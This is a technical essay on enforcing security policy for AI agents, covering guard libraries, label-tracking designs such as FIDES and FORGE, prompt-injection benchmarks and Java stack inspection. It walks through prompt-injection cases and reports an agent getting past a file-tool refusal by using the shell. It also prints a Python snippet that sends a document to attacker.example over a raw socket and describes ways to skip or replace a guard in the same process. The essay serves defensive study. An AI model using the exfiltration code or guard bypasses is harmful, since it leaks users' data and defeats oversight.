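# Library-level versus interpreter-level enforcement of agent security policy

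## Where an agent's actions can be checked

Library-level and interpreter-level enforcement are two ways to make an AI agent follow a security policy. An agent is a program in which a language model chooses actions, either by calling tools (functions that search files, send email or move money) or by writing code that calls them. A policy is a rule stating which actions the agent may take, with which data and on whose authority. Enforcement must happen between the model's choice and the action, usually in one of four places. A guard library wraps the tools in checks written in the host language, which is the language of the application. An interpreter runs the code that the agent writes and can apply the policy at every step. A typed or capability language limits what a program can reach, often before it runs. A sandbox works outside the language, isolating the agent with the operating system,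 a virtual machine or a similar runtime.

Operating system designers faced much the same problem around 1970, when organisations wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. Agents add a difficulty because an attacker does not need an account on the machine, only a way to put a sentence where the agent will read it.

### From a request to an action

A language model only produces text. In OpenAI's *Function calling* guide, the application sends the model a request and a list of tools, each with a name and a description of its arguments. The model may answer with a tool call, such as a call to a weather function with Paris as the location. The application runs the matching function and sends back the output, and this repeats until the model replies with an answer instead of a call. A tool call is therefore a proposal, and a check can run just before application code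 carries it out.

Alternatively, the model can write a program that calls the tools. Anthropic's *Programmatic tool calling* describes a version in which Claude writes Python that runs in an isolated container. Whenever the code calls a tool function, execution pauses until the application receives the call and returns the result. For example, one script can find which of 20 employees have overspent, replacing 20 trips through the model and keeping thousands of expense lines out of its context. The application can still inspect each tool call, but the code that runs between calls can do whatever the container permits.

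Consider the request "send Bob the document he asked for; his address is in the meeting notes". An agent that writes code might turn it into this:

```python
notes    = find_file("meeting notes")
title    = ask_reader("Which document did Bob ask for?", notes)
address  = ask_reader("What is Bob's email address?", notes)
document = fetch_file(title)
send_email(to=address, attachment=document)
```

Here `ask_reader` sends a question and a piece of text to a language model and returns its answer. An agent that issues tool calls one at a time would take much the same steps, but the model would choose each one after reading the previous result.

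### How a note can change the recipient

Prompt injection is text that an attacker plants in data an agent reads, hoping the model will obey it as an instruction. Suppose the attacker can edit the meeting notes and adds an instruction to give Bob's address as one the attacker controls. The program above still runs the same five steps in the same order. Only the value of `address` differs, so the document goes to the attacker. A second instruction could change `title`, letting the attacker choose the document too.

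The example comes from the Google DeepMind paper that introduced CaMeL, an agent design with an interpreter that tracks the source of every value. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, attributes the underlying weakness to the fact that models receive the user's trusted words and the untrusted contents of a file in one stream of tokens, with no known way to reliably make them follow the user's instructions while treating the file only as data.

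The planted line need not look like an instruction. "Bob has a new address" would be enough. *AutoDojo* (2026), a benchmark that optimises injections against whatever defence it is testing, found that attacks succeed far more often when the user lets content an attacker can reach determine parameters or actions, and that strong content filters do not prevent this. The request about Bob is an example, since the user relies on the notes for the address.

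A developer could train or instruct the model to be more suspicious, which helps but gives no guarantee. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) argues that a model without a reliable boundary between instructions and data cannot be guaranteed to refuse injected instructions, however much training or filtering it gets. It cites Anthropic's figures for an older model, Claude Opus 4.5, in coding environments, where attacks succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred. Newer models resist the old fixed attacks almost completely, but in *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (2026), Kurakin, Karande and colleagues used a swarm of attacking agents to adapt the injected text and got past even the most robust models they tested.

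Some direct evidence supports moving the check out of the model. *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026) reports on nine defence configurations and more than 20,000 attacks from a program that learned from its failures. Every defence that relied on the model to protect itself eventually broke. A filter in application code, which inspected each response before the user received it, let nothing through in 15,000 attacks. Catching known secrets in text is easier than judging arbitrary actions, so the result is stronger evidence about where to put a check than about how well that filter would work for an agent.

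### The reference monitor

The standard account of what such a check requires comes from *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), a report to the US Air Force on how users with different clearances could share a machine when any of them might be a hostile programmer. The report's central idea is the reference monitor, which checks every reference a program makes to data, a device or another program against a list of the references that program may make. One can picture the list as a matrix with a row for each user or program, a column for each resource, and entries such as READ or WRITE.

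Anderson set three requirements for any mechanism that implements the idea:

- It must be tamper-proof. If the program under control can alter the check, the check is worthless.
- It must always be invoked. If some programs are exempt, those programs become part of the security apparatus and have to meet the same requirements.
- It must be small enough for complete analysis and testing. Otherwise nobody can know that it works in every case.

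The report applied these requirements to a commercial system, the HIS 635 computer with its GCOS III operating system. The hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory. For input and output, however, the program called on GCOS III, which acted for the user with that confinement switched off, so the hardware check was not always invoked. GCOS III could not serve as the monitor either. With its supporting software, it had between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many to analyse completely, and testers had already broken into it several times. The size problem recurs with agents. The trusted base is all the code that must be correct for a policy to hold, so if a check relies on a large runtime, that runtime is part of the trusted base.

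*Ring-0 by Default* (Li, Huang and colleagues, 2026) applied Anderson's requirements to current agent defences. Rules in the system prompt, the developer's standing instructions to the model, fail all three. The model may not follow them, injected text in the same input can override them, and nobody can establish in advance how they will affect a neural network. Defences outside the model did better. Hooks that intercept tool calls, for example, met the first two requirements and partly met the third, while host sandboxes met all three. These results apply only to the path each mechanism covers, and an agent may have other paths.

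### Mediation and visibility

Mediation means that no action can reach the outside world without passing the check. It is Anderson's second requirement, and in agents it fails easily. Li and colleagues tested three coding agents, Claude Code, Codex CLI and Gemini CLI. Gemini CLI's file tool refused to write outside the agent's workspace, but its shell tool, in the permission mode called "bypass", would write to the same place. When a real model was given the task, with no attacker involved, it wrote the file through the shell in all five runs, in four of them after the file tool had refused.

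Agents that write code have even more ways to bypass a check. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) describes an agent that compiles bibliographies under a policy that every entry must come from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The developer supplies a function that appends DBLP entries to a file. An agent with an ordinary code interpreter can ignore that function, make up an entry, and save it with the standard library's file-writing function. The developer could instead remove the interpreter and offer a single tool that fetches an entry and writes it in one step. This would prevent the agent from adding made-up entries, but the agent could no longer sort or filter the results with code, and the model would have to read them one by one.

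A library's claim to mediate every action usually depends on something outside the library to block other paths. *Causality Laundering* (2026) presents a proxy that examines every call between a model and its tool server, but the proxy sees every action only if the deployment leaves no path around it. *Proof-Carrying Contracts* (2026) states more generally that mediation is complete only if the agent has no other way to act, and that isolation removes the other ways.

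Even under complete mediation, where a check runs before every action, the check may lack the information it needs. The information available to it when it decides is its visibility. *Kairos* (2026) describes a monitor at the boundary where data enters and leaves the agent's machine. The monitor runs on every event in both directions, but it can only approximate where the data in an outgoing message came from. If it can only allow or refuse, it has to err by either blocking legitimate work or letting attacks through.

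The information available for checking the email to Bob depends on where the check runs. A sandbox can detect only a network connection to a mail server, which looks the same whichever address the message carries. A guard library around `send_email` receives the address and the attachment and can compare the address with a contact list, but the address arrives as a plain string with no record of where it came from. An interpreter that executes all five lines can record that the address came from the notes. A type checker can establish this before the program runs if text from an untrusted file has its own type, but it can't determine which address the notes will contain.

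| Where the check sits | Mediation: can code get round it? | Visibility: what can the check see? |
|---|---|---|
| Guard library | Yes, if the agent's code can reach the file system or network directly; no, if wrapped tools are its only way to act | The tool's name and arguments, normally without their origin |
| Interpreter | Only through a flaw in the interpreter or an unguarded function that it exposes | Each operation and, if the interpreter keeps track, the origin of every value |
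| Typed or capability language | Only through unsafe features that the language leaves open | The types, effects or permissions in the program, often before it runs |
| Sandbox | Only through a flaw in the isolation or a permission that is too broad | Files, processes and network connections, with little of their meaning |

These places can be combined. A guard library inside a sandbox keeps its visibility, and the sandbox can block the paths that would bypass it. Anderson's other two requirements apply in every row, but they are hardest to meet for the interpreter, because it adds a substantial piece of software to the trusted base.

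### The dual-LLM pattern and the hole it leaves

*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposes an early design that divides the work between two models to guard against a confused deputy, a program that someone with less authority tricks into misusing its own. A privileged model takes the user's request, plans the steps and can call tools, but never reads untrusted content. A quarantined model reads the untrusted content and has no tools. A controller, which is ordinary software, runs the tools and stores their results and the quarantined model's answers in variables with names such as `$VAR1`. The privileged model works only with these names, unless the controller can verify a quarantined model's answer, such as a choice from a fixed list of categories. The privileged model may then receive that answer directly.

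For the request about Bob, the privileged model would write the five-line program and the quarantined model would answer the two `ask_reader` questions. A malicious note cannot add a step, because only the quarantined model reads it and that model has no tools. The note can still corrupt an answer. If the quarantined model returns the attacker's address, the controller stores it in a variable and `send_email` uses that variable as planned. The pattern protects the control flow (which steps run and in what order) but not the data flow. Willison credits the CaMeL paper with finding this flaw. He had already called the original proposal "pretty bad" because it makes an assistant much more complicated to build, and because a single mistake that leaks untrusted text to the privileged model undoes the protection.

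### Labels and capabilities

Closing the hole requires tracking values. A label is metadata on a value or a computation that records where data came from or who may read it. If `notes` carries the label "from a shared file", then `address`, which derives from `notes`, inherits the label and still carries it when the program calls `send_email`. Information-flow control follows labels through a computation and blocks forbidden flows. Some of its rules concern integrity, such as the rule that data from an untrusted source must not authorise a sensitive action. Others concern confidentiality, such as Zhou and colleagues' example that data from customer A should never go to customer B.

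Both kinds of rule apply to Bob's email, but labels alone cannot distinguish his real address from an attacker's, because both come from the notes. A rule that blocks every recipient taken from an untrusted file will stop the attacker, but it will also stop the user from getting the job done. The policy needs another fact, such as whether the address is in the user's contacts or whether its owner already has access to the document. Failing that, the system can ask the user, though Willison worries that people who face constant requests for approval learn to click yes.

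*The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) defines a capability as an unforgeable ticket that proves its holder may access the object it names. The reference is itself the permission, so code without the reference cannot request access. In a modern Haskell example from Zhou and colleagues, file functions accept only a value of type `Path`, which stands for authority over one directory and everything beneath it. A program can narrow a `Path` to a single file but cannot widen it, and a program that passes the string "/etc/passwd" instead of a `Path` fails to compile.

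CaMeL is short for "CApabilities for MachinE Learning", but its "capabilities" are tags on values that record the source of the data and its permitted readers, which makes them labels by the definitions above. A label blocks nothing unless a policy reads it at the right moment and refuses the action. With a capability, somebody decides earlier, when choosing whether to hand over the reference. A mail tool that can only write to Bob's known address would be a capability, and no planted note could redirect it, but someone would have to know the address before the agent started. In the example nobody does, which is why the user mentioned the notes.

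### AgentDojo

Most published comparisons of these designs use the same benchmark, *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024). *AgentDojo* has four simulated environments, each with its own tools and data. A user task is an ordinary request, such as paying a bill in a named file. An injection task is an attacker's goal, such as sending as much money as possible to the attacker's account. The benchmark puts the attack text in data that the agent will read while working on the user's task. Within each environment, it pairs every user task with every injection task, and each pair is one security case.

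| Suite | Tools | User tasks | Injection tasks | Security cases |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace (email, calendar, files) | 24 | 40 | 6 | 240 |
| Slack (messages, web pages) | 11 | 21 | 5 | 105 |
| Travel (flights, hotels, restaurants) | 28 | 20 | 7 | 140 |
| Banking (payments, statements) | 11 | 16 | 9 | 144 |

That makes 97 user tasks and 629 cases in the first version. Later results often use a different denominator. *SecOPD* (2026) counts 949 cases in version 1.2.1, with all the growth in Workspace, which now has 560. A U.S. Department of Commerce catalogue entry partly explains the growth. It describes a modified copy of AgentDojo that added Workspace attacks on large amounts of data. The main project has since adopted these attacks.

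Ordinary code scores each run by inspecting the agent's output and the state of the environment, such as whether the payment went out and to whom. Debenedetti and colleagues avoided using a language model as judge because an injection good enough to fool the agent might fool the judge too. There are three scores. Benign utility is the share of user tasks that the agent completes when nobody is attacking. Utility under attack is the share of security cases in which it completes the user's task without adversarial side effects. The targeted attack success rate is the share in which the attacker's goal is achieved. An agent that refuses to do anything has a perfect attack success rate of zero, so a security score means little without a utility score. The last two scores don't have to add up to 100%, since an agent can fail at both the user's task and the attacker's.

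*Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) points out that some of the benchmark's injections overwrite content that the user's task needs. In one case the attack text replaces the details of the bill the user wants to pay, so no agent could complete the task, and utility under attack falls for a reason unrelated to the defence. Evaluations also tend to use one fixed attack message, which according to *AutoDojo* overstates the protection that most defences give. I expect this to matter less for a deterministic check outside the model, since a rule that blocks recipients taken from the notes gives the same result however the attacker words the injection.

 

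AgentDojo has two further limits that matter when choosing between levels. First, many of its tasks allow an agent to settle its plan before reading any data, which suits designs like the dual-LLM pattern. *AgentDyn* (2026) follows AgentDojo's scheme, but its 60 user tasks and 560 security cases in shopping, GitHub and daily life all require the agent to plan as it goes. Second, an AgentDojo agent acts only through the tools of its suite, so the original benchmark tests what information a check has access to far more than whether code can bypass the check. The modified copy in the Commerce Department's catalogue partly fills that gap with a terminal environment, where attacks try to make the agent run code chosen by the attacker.

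## Guard libraries around tool calls

The wrapper that a guard library puts around a tool has the same name and arguments as the tool, so the model can use it in the same way, but it consults a policy before calling the real function. For `send_email` it might look like this:

```python
def send_email(to, attachment):
    call = {"tool": "send_email", "to": to, "attachment": attachment}
    decision = policy.decide(call, context)
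    if decision == ALLOW:
        return real_send_email(to, attachment)
    if decision == ASK and user_approves(call):
        return real_send_email(to, attachment)
    return "Refused: " + policy.reason(call, context)
```

Designs differ mainly in what `context` contains. It can be empty, a short label that summarises everything the model has read, or a full record of past events.

### One guarded call

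For example, an agent that issues tool calls one at a time has found and read the meeting notes and fetched the document. Its model now proposes a call to `send_email`.

First, the application can check the proposed call against the tool's schema, which catches a missing argument or a number where there should be text. But as Santos-Grueiro (2026) points out in *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents*, a well-formed call can still carry values that an attacker chose. For example, the attacker's email address would pass this check just as Bob's would.

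Next, the wrapper gathers whatever else the policy needs, such as the user's identity or the earlier calls. It should get these facts from the application, not from the model, because an injection could make the model claim that the user has already approved the email. *Runtime Authorization Consistency Checking for MCP-based Agentic Workflows* (Zhang, Lee and colleagues, 2026) presents a guard called RAC that follows this principle. RAC takes the user's identity from the login session and the type of action from the tool's declaration, and it ignores the model's explanation of the call.

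A policy engine then decides whether to allow the call. The engine is usually ordinary code, so the same call in the same context always gets the same answer. If the call is allowed, the wrapper runs the tool and returns the result. If not, the wrapper can stop the agent, ask the user, or return an error message so that the model can try something else. Some products use a model in this step. According to Anthropic's documentation, when "auto mode" is on in the coding agent Claude Code, a classifier reviews actions in place of the user.

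An agent can still complete its task after a guard refuses a tool call. In *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026) used their guard, FORGE, to enforce an airline's and a retailer's rules on customer-service agents. Averaged over three models, the share of successful trials rose from 74.7% to 81.5% for the airline and from 86.3% to 87.4% for the retailer. Most of the gains came from tasks in which FORGE had refused at least one call.

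### Progent: rules for each tool

The simplest kind of policy considers only the proposed call. Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, write such policies as lists of rules. Each rule names a tool, allows or forbids it, and sets conditions on its arguments, such as membership of a list or a match with a text pattern. Progent tries the "forbid" rules first, then the "allow" rules, and refuses any call that matches neither. A policy for the request about Bob could be:

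```
allow  find_file   when { name == "meeting notes" }
allow  fetch_file  when { true }
forbid send_email  when { not (to in ["bob@acme.example", "ana@acme.example"]) },
                   fallback: ask the user
allow  send_email  when { true }
```

If the notes contain the attacker's address, the third rule sends the question to the user. If they contain Bob's usual address, the email goes out. If Bob really has changed his address, the user gets the same question as in the attack, because the rule only compares `to` with a list. The policy also doesn't restrict `title`, so a planted note could still make the agent send Bob the wrong document.

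Writing rules like these for every request is tedious, so Progent has a language model write the first policy from the user's request, before the agent reads anything else. As the agent learns more, the model proposes updates. The model may have read an injection by then, so Progent checks each update with ordinary code. Let A(P) be the set of calls that policy P allows. A new policy P′ takes effect automatically only if A(P′) ⊆ A(P), meaning that it allows nothing new. An SMT solver, a program that determines whether a logical formula can be satisfied, tests this by looking for a call that P′ allows and P does not. If it finds one, the update is an expansion and needs approval. On AgentDojo, only 6% of updates were expansions.

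The request about Bob shows that narrowing a policy can be unsafe, although Shi and colleagues treat every narrowing as safe. The user never stated an address, so the first policy might allow email to anyone. After reading the tampered notes, the model could propose restricting `send_email` to the address it found there. Because this narrows the policy, it would take effect without approval, and the agent could then email only the attacker. The subset test guarantees only that the agent gains no new powers, so it can't ensure that the remaining ones are the right ones.

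With GPT-4o as both agent and policy writer, Progent cut the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0%. On ASB, another benchmark of injection attacks, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. The number of completed tasks changed little on either benchmark. All policy expansions in these runs were approved automatically to simulate a careless user, so the results show how well the model writes policies, not how much the subset test adds. On AgentDojo, the first policy without updates cut the rate to 2.5%, and having a person review the first policy and every expansion cut it to 0%.

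*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that Progent's guarantees are only as good as its policies, and that planted text in a tool result may lead an update to relax those policies. The subset test answers the second objection only if someone is there to reject bad expansions. Progent's scope also excludes attacks that change only what the agent tells the user and attacks that stay within the permitted calls, for example by steering a purchase towards the attacker's product.

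### FIDES: a label on the whole context

The guard could make a better decision about Bob's email if it had a record that the agent had read an untrusted file. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) adds this record to the planning loop, the code that sends the conversation to the model and runs the calls the model proposes. Its system, FIDES, labels every tool result with whether its source is trusted and who may read the result.

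The conversation has a label too, which combines the labels of all its messages. It is untrusted if any message is untrusted. Its permitted readers are the people who may read every message, so if the messages have reader sets R₁ to Rₙ, the conversation's readers are R₁ ∩ R₂ ∩ … ∩ Rₙ. Nobody can reliably tell which messages influenced a model's output, so a call that the model writes inherits the label of the whole conversation. The loop compares this label with the policy just before the call runs. For Bob's email, the policy could be:

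```
send_email(to, attachment) may run only if
    1. the call itself is trusted
    2. the value of "to" is trusted
    3. the recipient may read the attachment
```

An ordinary agent fails the first two conditions as soon as it reads the notes. This stops the attack, but also the email to the real Bob.

It stops much else besides. The notes stay in the conversation, so the conversation stays untrusted, and the loop refuses every later call that requires trust, even one that has nothing to do with the notes. This is called label creep. Confidentiality creeps in the same way, because each new message can only shrink the set of permitted readers. Costa and colleagues measured the cost on AgentDojo with GPT-4o and no attacks:

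| Suite | Ordinary agent, no checks | Ordinary agent with checks | FIDES with checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

With checks on, the ordinary agent completed about half as many Workspace tasks as before and about a fifth as many Slack tasks. Travel is an exception because the policy lets many Travel tools run in an untrusted conversation, provided no confidential data leaks.

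### Keeping data in variables

FIDES addresses label creep by building on Willison's dual-LLM pattern. When a tool result would make the conversation's label more restrictive, FIDES stores the result in a variable and shows the planning model only the variable's name. It can do this field by field, so an email's trusted date can stay visible while its body goes into a variable. In Willison's pattern, by contrast, the controller withholds tool results from the privileged model by default.

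The planning model can pass a variable to a tool without reading it. It can also call `query_llm`, which sends an isolated model a question about the variable and stores the answer in another variable. If the planning model must read the contents, it can call `inspect`, but the conversation then takes on the variable's label.

For Bob's email, the agent would make these calls:

```
find_file("meeting notes")                                     -> #notes
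query_llm("Which document did Bob ask for?", #notes)           -> #title
query_llm("What is Bob's email address?", #notes)              -> #address
fetch_file(#title)                                             -> #document
send_email(to=#address, attachment=#document)
```

The planning model has read nothing untrusted, so the call meets the first condition. The call still fails the second, because the address came from the notes and carries their label. Variables prevent label creep, but they can't help when the action depends on untrusted data. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) reports the same problem in a design whose planner never reads tool results. Turning on the label checks cut the share of AgentDojo tasks it completed from 53.0% to 29.0%, mainly because the plans passed untrusted results to actions that required trusted ones.

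To make the request about Bob work, the developer would have to drop the second condition and rely on the third, which lets the email go only to someone who is already allowed to read the document. That rules out the attacker unless the attacker has access too. The recipient must also be allowed to read the notes, because `#title` came from them and a tool result inherits the labels of the tool's arguments.

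Other tasks need the data to choose the next step, such as "if someone has emailed me about a meeting, put it in my calendar". Here FIDES can force the isolated model to answer only true or false. A policy may accept that answer because an attacker controls only one bit. The attacker could still cause a false "yes", but could not use the answer to insert a new instruction. Costa and colleagues left this feature out of their AgentDojo tests because most of the tasks didn't need it.

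In those tests, 152 attacks succeeded against the ordinary agent without checks, 21 against FIDES without checks and none against FIDES with checks. These counts exclude cases that AgentDojo misjudged, which the researchers removed manually. No attacks succeeded against FIDES with checks partly because the researchers marked a data field as untrusted if at least one of AgentDojo's attacks used it. A real deployment has no list of attacks to work from, so it must label data by general facts, such as who sent an email. An attack through a field wrongly labelled as trusted would pass the checks.

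FIDES also allows one kind of leak by design. An observer who can see which tools the agent calls may learn something about the secret data that led to those calls. Preventing this would require noninterference, the guarantee that secret inputs don't change visible outputs. Costa and colleagues judged noninterference too restrictive because it would forbid almost any visible action after the agent had read a secret.

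### FORGE: rules over past events

FORGE records each message, tool call and tool result as a node in a graph, with an arrow from one event to another that may depend on it. Policies are written in Datalog, a query language whose rules derive new facts from known ones. A rule can refer to itself, so it can follow a chain of dependencies of any length. Before each action, FORGE waits until the graph contains everything the action depends on, then evaluates the rules. If any rule derives `Deny`, FORGE blocks the action, even if another rule derives `Allow`.

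A FORGE-style policy for Bob's email could be:

```
Untrusted(e)    :- FromSharedFile(e).
Untrusted(e)    :- DependsOn(e, d), Untrusted(d).
Approved(a, r)  :- DependsOn(a, u), UserApproves(u, r).
Deny(a)         :- EmailTo(a, r), Untrusted(a), not Approved(a, r).
```

The first two lines mark as untrusted anything that came from a shared file, directly or through other events. The last line blocks an untrusted email unless an earlier message from the user approves that recipient. The agent would have to ask the user "Shall I send this to bob@acme.example?" and try again after the user answers. An email that doesn't depend on a shared file needs no approval.

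FORGE's graph links a model's reply to every message in its conversation, because the reply could depend on any of them. For a single agent with one long conversation, distrust therefore spreads just as it does with FIDES's label. The graph's advantage is that a rule can combine these links with other facts, including the order of events. In one case study, Palumbo and colleagues stop a coding agent from publishing its changes unless a security scan has passed since the latest edit. A rule that considers only the current call could not express this, because the publish command is the same whether or not the scan has passed.

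History also matters when each call looks acceptable on its own. In Zhang and colleagues' example, a user asks an assistant to find free slots in a calendar. The assistant reads the calendar, searches related emails, then messages someone about rescheduling. It has standing permission to use all these tools, but the user asked only for free slots. On 1,008 test workflows that a guard should have blocked, RAC missed none, while the best simpler check missed 509. The researchers built these workflows from the same kinds of violation that RAC's rules cover, so the results on plans written by language models are more informative. RAC caught 92.8% of the violations in those plans, and the simpler check caught 68.8%.

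### FORGE against a data theft attack

Palumbo and colleagues tested FORGE on an agent that could list files, read them and send email. The files ranged from unclassified to top secret, and each recipient had a clearance. In the attack scenario, the user asked for a summary of a company's conflicts of interest. The file on that company contained a fake system update with instructions to email top-secret merger plans to an outside auditor, supposedly because a compliance audit required it. In the harmless scenario, the agent had to summarise a quarterly report for a colleague.

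The researchers compared three FORGE configurations with an agent whose only safeguard was a prompt telling it not to leak data. Two configurations used the classic military rules, under which the agent may not read above its clearance or write to anyone with a lower clearance. The third, called "toxic flow", allowed all reading but blocked email to outsiders once both untrusted and sensitive data had entered the agent's context. Each configuration ran five times on GPT-4.1-mini.

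| Configuration | Thefts | Harmless task completed | What FORGE blocked during the attacks | Mean time |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Prompt only | 5 of 5 | 5 of 5 | Nothing (not in use) | 5.3 s |
| Clearance rules, agent cleared for top secret | 0 of 5 | 5 of 5 | 9 emails | 7.9 s |
| Clearance rules, agent cleared for secret | 0 of 5 | 5 of 5 | 9 file listings, 2 emails | 7.6 s |
| Toxic flow | 0 of 5 | 5 of 5 | 6 emails | 11.1 s |

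The blocked emails show that the injection was still fooling the model and that FORGE, not the model, prevented the theft. The perfect score on the harmless task is weaker evidence because the task did not test how often the rules block legitimate work. The colleague had enough clearance, and no outsider or untrusted file was involved. The rule on writing, for example, compares the recipient's clearance with the agent's rather than with the document's classification, so an agent cleared for top secret could not email even an unclassified file to someone with a lower clearance.

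Results on AgentDojo give a better idea of how many tasks label creep prevents an agent from completing. Palumbo and colleagues expressed FIDES's policy in FORGE and compared it with their own policy, which checks whether the user asked for an action and where its target came from. Both ran on AgentDojo's standard agent, so FIDES's rules had to work without FIDES's variables. In runs that also repeated the user's request after each batch of tool results, the agent completed 33.2% of tasks under FIDES's rules, 62.5% under the new policy and 83.7% with neither policy. Attack success rates were 0.6%, 0.9% and 14.1%, respectively. Much of the loss from label creep therefore comes from rules that reject every consequential call in an untrusted conversation. Someone has to write more specific rules, but they recovered about half of the lost tasks with almost the same protection.

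### When the agent can write code

All these results assume that the agent cannot bypass the wrapper. This is easy to ensure if the agent can only call tools, because the application looks up each tool that the model names, and every name maps to a wrapper. A planted note may cause the model to try to open a network connection, but it cannot do so unless a tool provides that ability.

Even then, the developer has to wrap every tool. Progent can run as a proxy between an agent and its external tool servers, which requires no change to the agent's code, but Shi and colleagues note that the proxy doesn't cover tools built into the agent. Their library version does, but it requires changing a few lines of the agent's code.

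An agent that writes ordinary Python can avoid the wrappers altogether:

```python
document = fetch_file("Q3 forecast")

import socket
connection = socket.create_connection(("attacker.example", 80))
connection.sendall(document.encode())
```

The first line calls a wrapped tool, and a guard might reasonably allow it. The rest uses Python's standard library to send the document to the attacker. It never calls `send_email`, so the guard doesn't check this step, whether the policy is a list of rules, a label or a Datalog program. Code that writes to disk can bypass the guard in the same way, as in Zhou and colleagues' example of the made-up bibliography entry.

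The developer can wrap more functions. FORGE also intercepts web requests made through two popular Python libraries, `requests` and `httpx`, but Palumbo and colleagues state that raw network sockets and direct input and output remain outside its control. To keep the guarantee, the developer would have to find and wrap every function that opens a connection, writes a file or starts another program.

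Agent code that runs in the same process as the guard can also tamper with it. Python wrappers often keep a reference to the original function in `__wrapped__`, so the agent could call `send_email.__wrapped__(...)` to skip the check. It could also replace the policy object with one that allows everything. This violates Anderson's requirement that the check be tamper-proof. Running the agent's code in an isolated process and keeping the wrappers outside it solves both problems, but then the isolation forces calls through the check, and the library only decides whether to allow them. Another solution is to use a language whose types prevent the code from bypassing the library.

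### Matching shell commands as strings

Many coding agents have a tool that runs shell commands. The wrapper receives every command, but only as a string, and the usual policy is a list of text patterns. Course slides from UT Austin give an example policy for Claude Code that allows commands starting with `git status`, requires user approval for `git push`, and denies `sudo`, which runs a command with administrator rights.

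Such rules are brittle because a shell command is a program, and many programs do the same thing. A pattern that blocks `cat secret.txt` does not match `head secret.txt` or `cat sec*.txt`, which can print the same file. A command's effect can also depend on things outside the string. For example, `./build.sh` does whatever the script contains, and the agent may have just written that script.

Zhou and colleagues describe a bug of this kind in Claude Code from March 2026. When a command had several parts joined with `&&`, the program compared only the first part with its list of denied commands. A better parser can fix that bug, but it can't catch their other example, in which the agent runs a one-line Python program that opens the forbidden file, because the guard would have to determine what arbitrary Python code does. Stricter patterns also require the user to approve long commands that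 are hard to read. Users usually think in terms of files, for example that the agent may change anything in one directory, and command patterns express such rules poorly.

Santos-Grueiro suggests treating shell text, database queries and code patches as actions in themselves, not as data inside an action, unless a validator limits what they can do. A developer can also replace the shell with narrower tools, such as one that runs the project's tests and takes no free text. Otherwise, patterns are mainly useful against accidents, as the UT Austin slides say. They apply to the command the agent submits, not to the processes the command starts.

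For those processes, Claude Code relies on a sandbox. According to a University of Vermont support page, the operating system enforces the sandbox's file restrictions on shell commands and everything they start, regardless of the command's text, but Claude Code's built-in file-reading tool is outside the sandbox and subject only to the permission rules. An administrator who wants to keep the agent away from a file therefore has to block it in both the sandbox settings and the permission rules.

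## Checks inserted by the runtime or by rewriting the program

A guard library gives no protection against code that can reach the network or the file system without calling it. One remedy is to put the checks inside the language's standard library, so that the ordinary function for opening a file checks the policy no matter what code calls it. Another is to add a check before each sensitive operation in the program before it runs. Either way, the program still runs on the language's usual runtime, so nobody has to write a new interpreter.

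Java was the main testing ground for both methods. In the 1990s, browsers ran Java applets, small programs that arrived with a web page. The Java virtual machine (JVM), which executes compiled Java programs, ran applets in the same process as trusted code.

### Stack inspection

When a Java program opens a file, the request usually passes through several methods. The call stack has one frame for each method that has started but not finished. Checking only the newest frame would be useless, because that frame belongs to Java's trusted library. An applet could get any file by calling the library, which would make the library a confused deputy.

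Stack inspection therefore checks the callers too. Wallach and Felten (1998), in *Understanding Java Stack Inspection*, give the algorithm that Netscape, Microsoft and Sun all used, with small variations:

```
check(resource):
    for frame in call_stack:                                # newest first
        if the policy forbids frame.code to use resource:   refuse
        if frame has enabled its privilege for resource:    allow
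        if frame has disabled its privilege for resource:   refuse
    allow                                                   # Netscape refused here
```

If an applet calls a library method that tries to write a file, the runtime searches the call stack past the library's frame, reaches the applet's frame and blocks the write.

Trusted code sometimes needs a resource that its caller may not use, so a frame can enable a privilege. Mullan and Buckley's *JEP 486* gives the example of an application that has no permission to read files but asks for the current time. Java's time code has to read a time zone file to answer, so it first enables its own privilege. The search then stops at its frame before reaching the application. The privilege ends when the method returns.

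In *Stack Inspection*, Fournet and Gordon write that this mechanism has "a complex and subtle semantics". It also misses the influence of code that has already finished, because the stack contains only code that is still running, as Pistoia, Banerjee and Naumann point out in *Beyond Stack Inspection*. If an untrusted plugin reads the meeting notes and returns an address for Bob, its frame is gone by the time trusted code calls `send_email`, so the check passes whatever the address is. The check also misses an attacker who only edited the notes, because that attacker never had a frame on the stack.

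### What the Security Manager asked of library authors

Java's Security Manager made these decisions. Its job was simple in Java 1.0, when the standard library had only eight packages, local code could do anything, and applets could not access files or the network. Java 1.2 replaced this with a more ambitious rule, under which all code was untrusted by default and users granted specific permissions to specific code.

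The new rule affected methods throughout the standard library. By Mullan and Buckley's count, over 1,000 methods had to check permissions and over 1,200 had to raise their own privileges, as the time code does. Java's maintainers had to review every change to these methods with the policy in mind, even though the Security Manager was off by default and very few applications turned it on.

Developers of other libraries also had trouble, because the check covers every caller on the stack. A library could read a file only if the application calling it also had permission to read it. The application's developer therefore had to grant the application permissions that it did not need for its own work. A library's developer could prevent this by enabling the library's privilege around the right operations, but *JEP 411* (Mullan, 2021) judges that most developers had far too little interest to learn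 the rules for doing so safely. It was easier to grant all permissions to all code.

Java also had no way to express a partial policy, such as "allow everything except reading files outside this directory". A developer who wanted only that restriction had to list every other permission the application needed, including writing files, because the Security Manager blocked anything not on the list. Permissions could also combine so that a series of individually safe operations had an effect that should have required a stronger permission.

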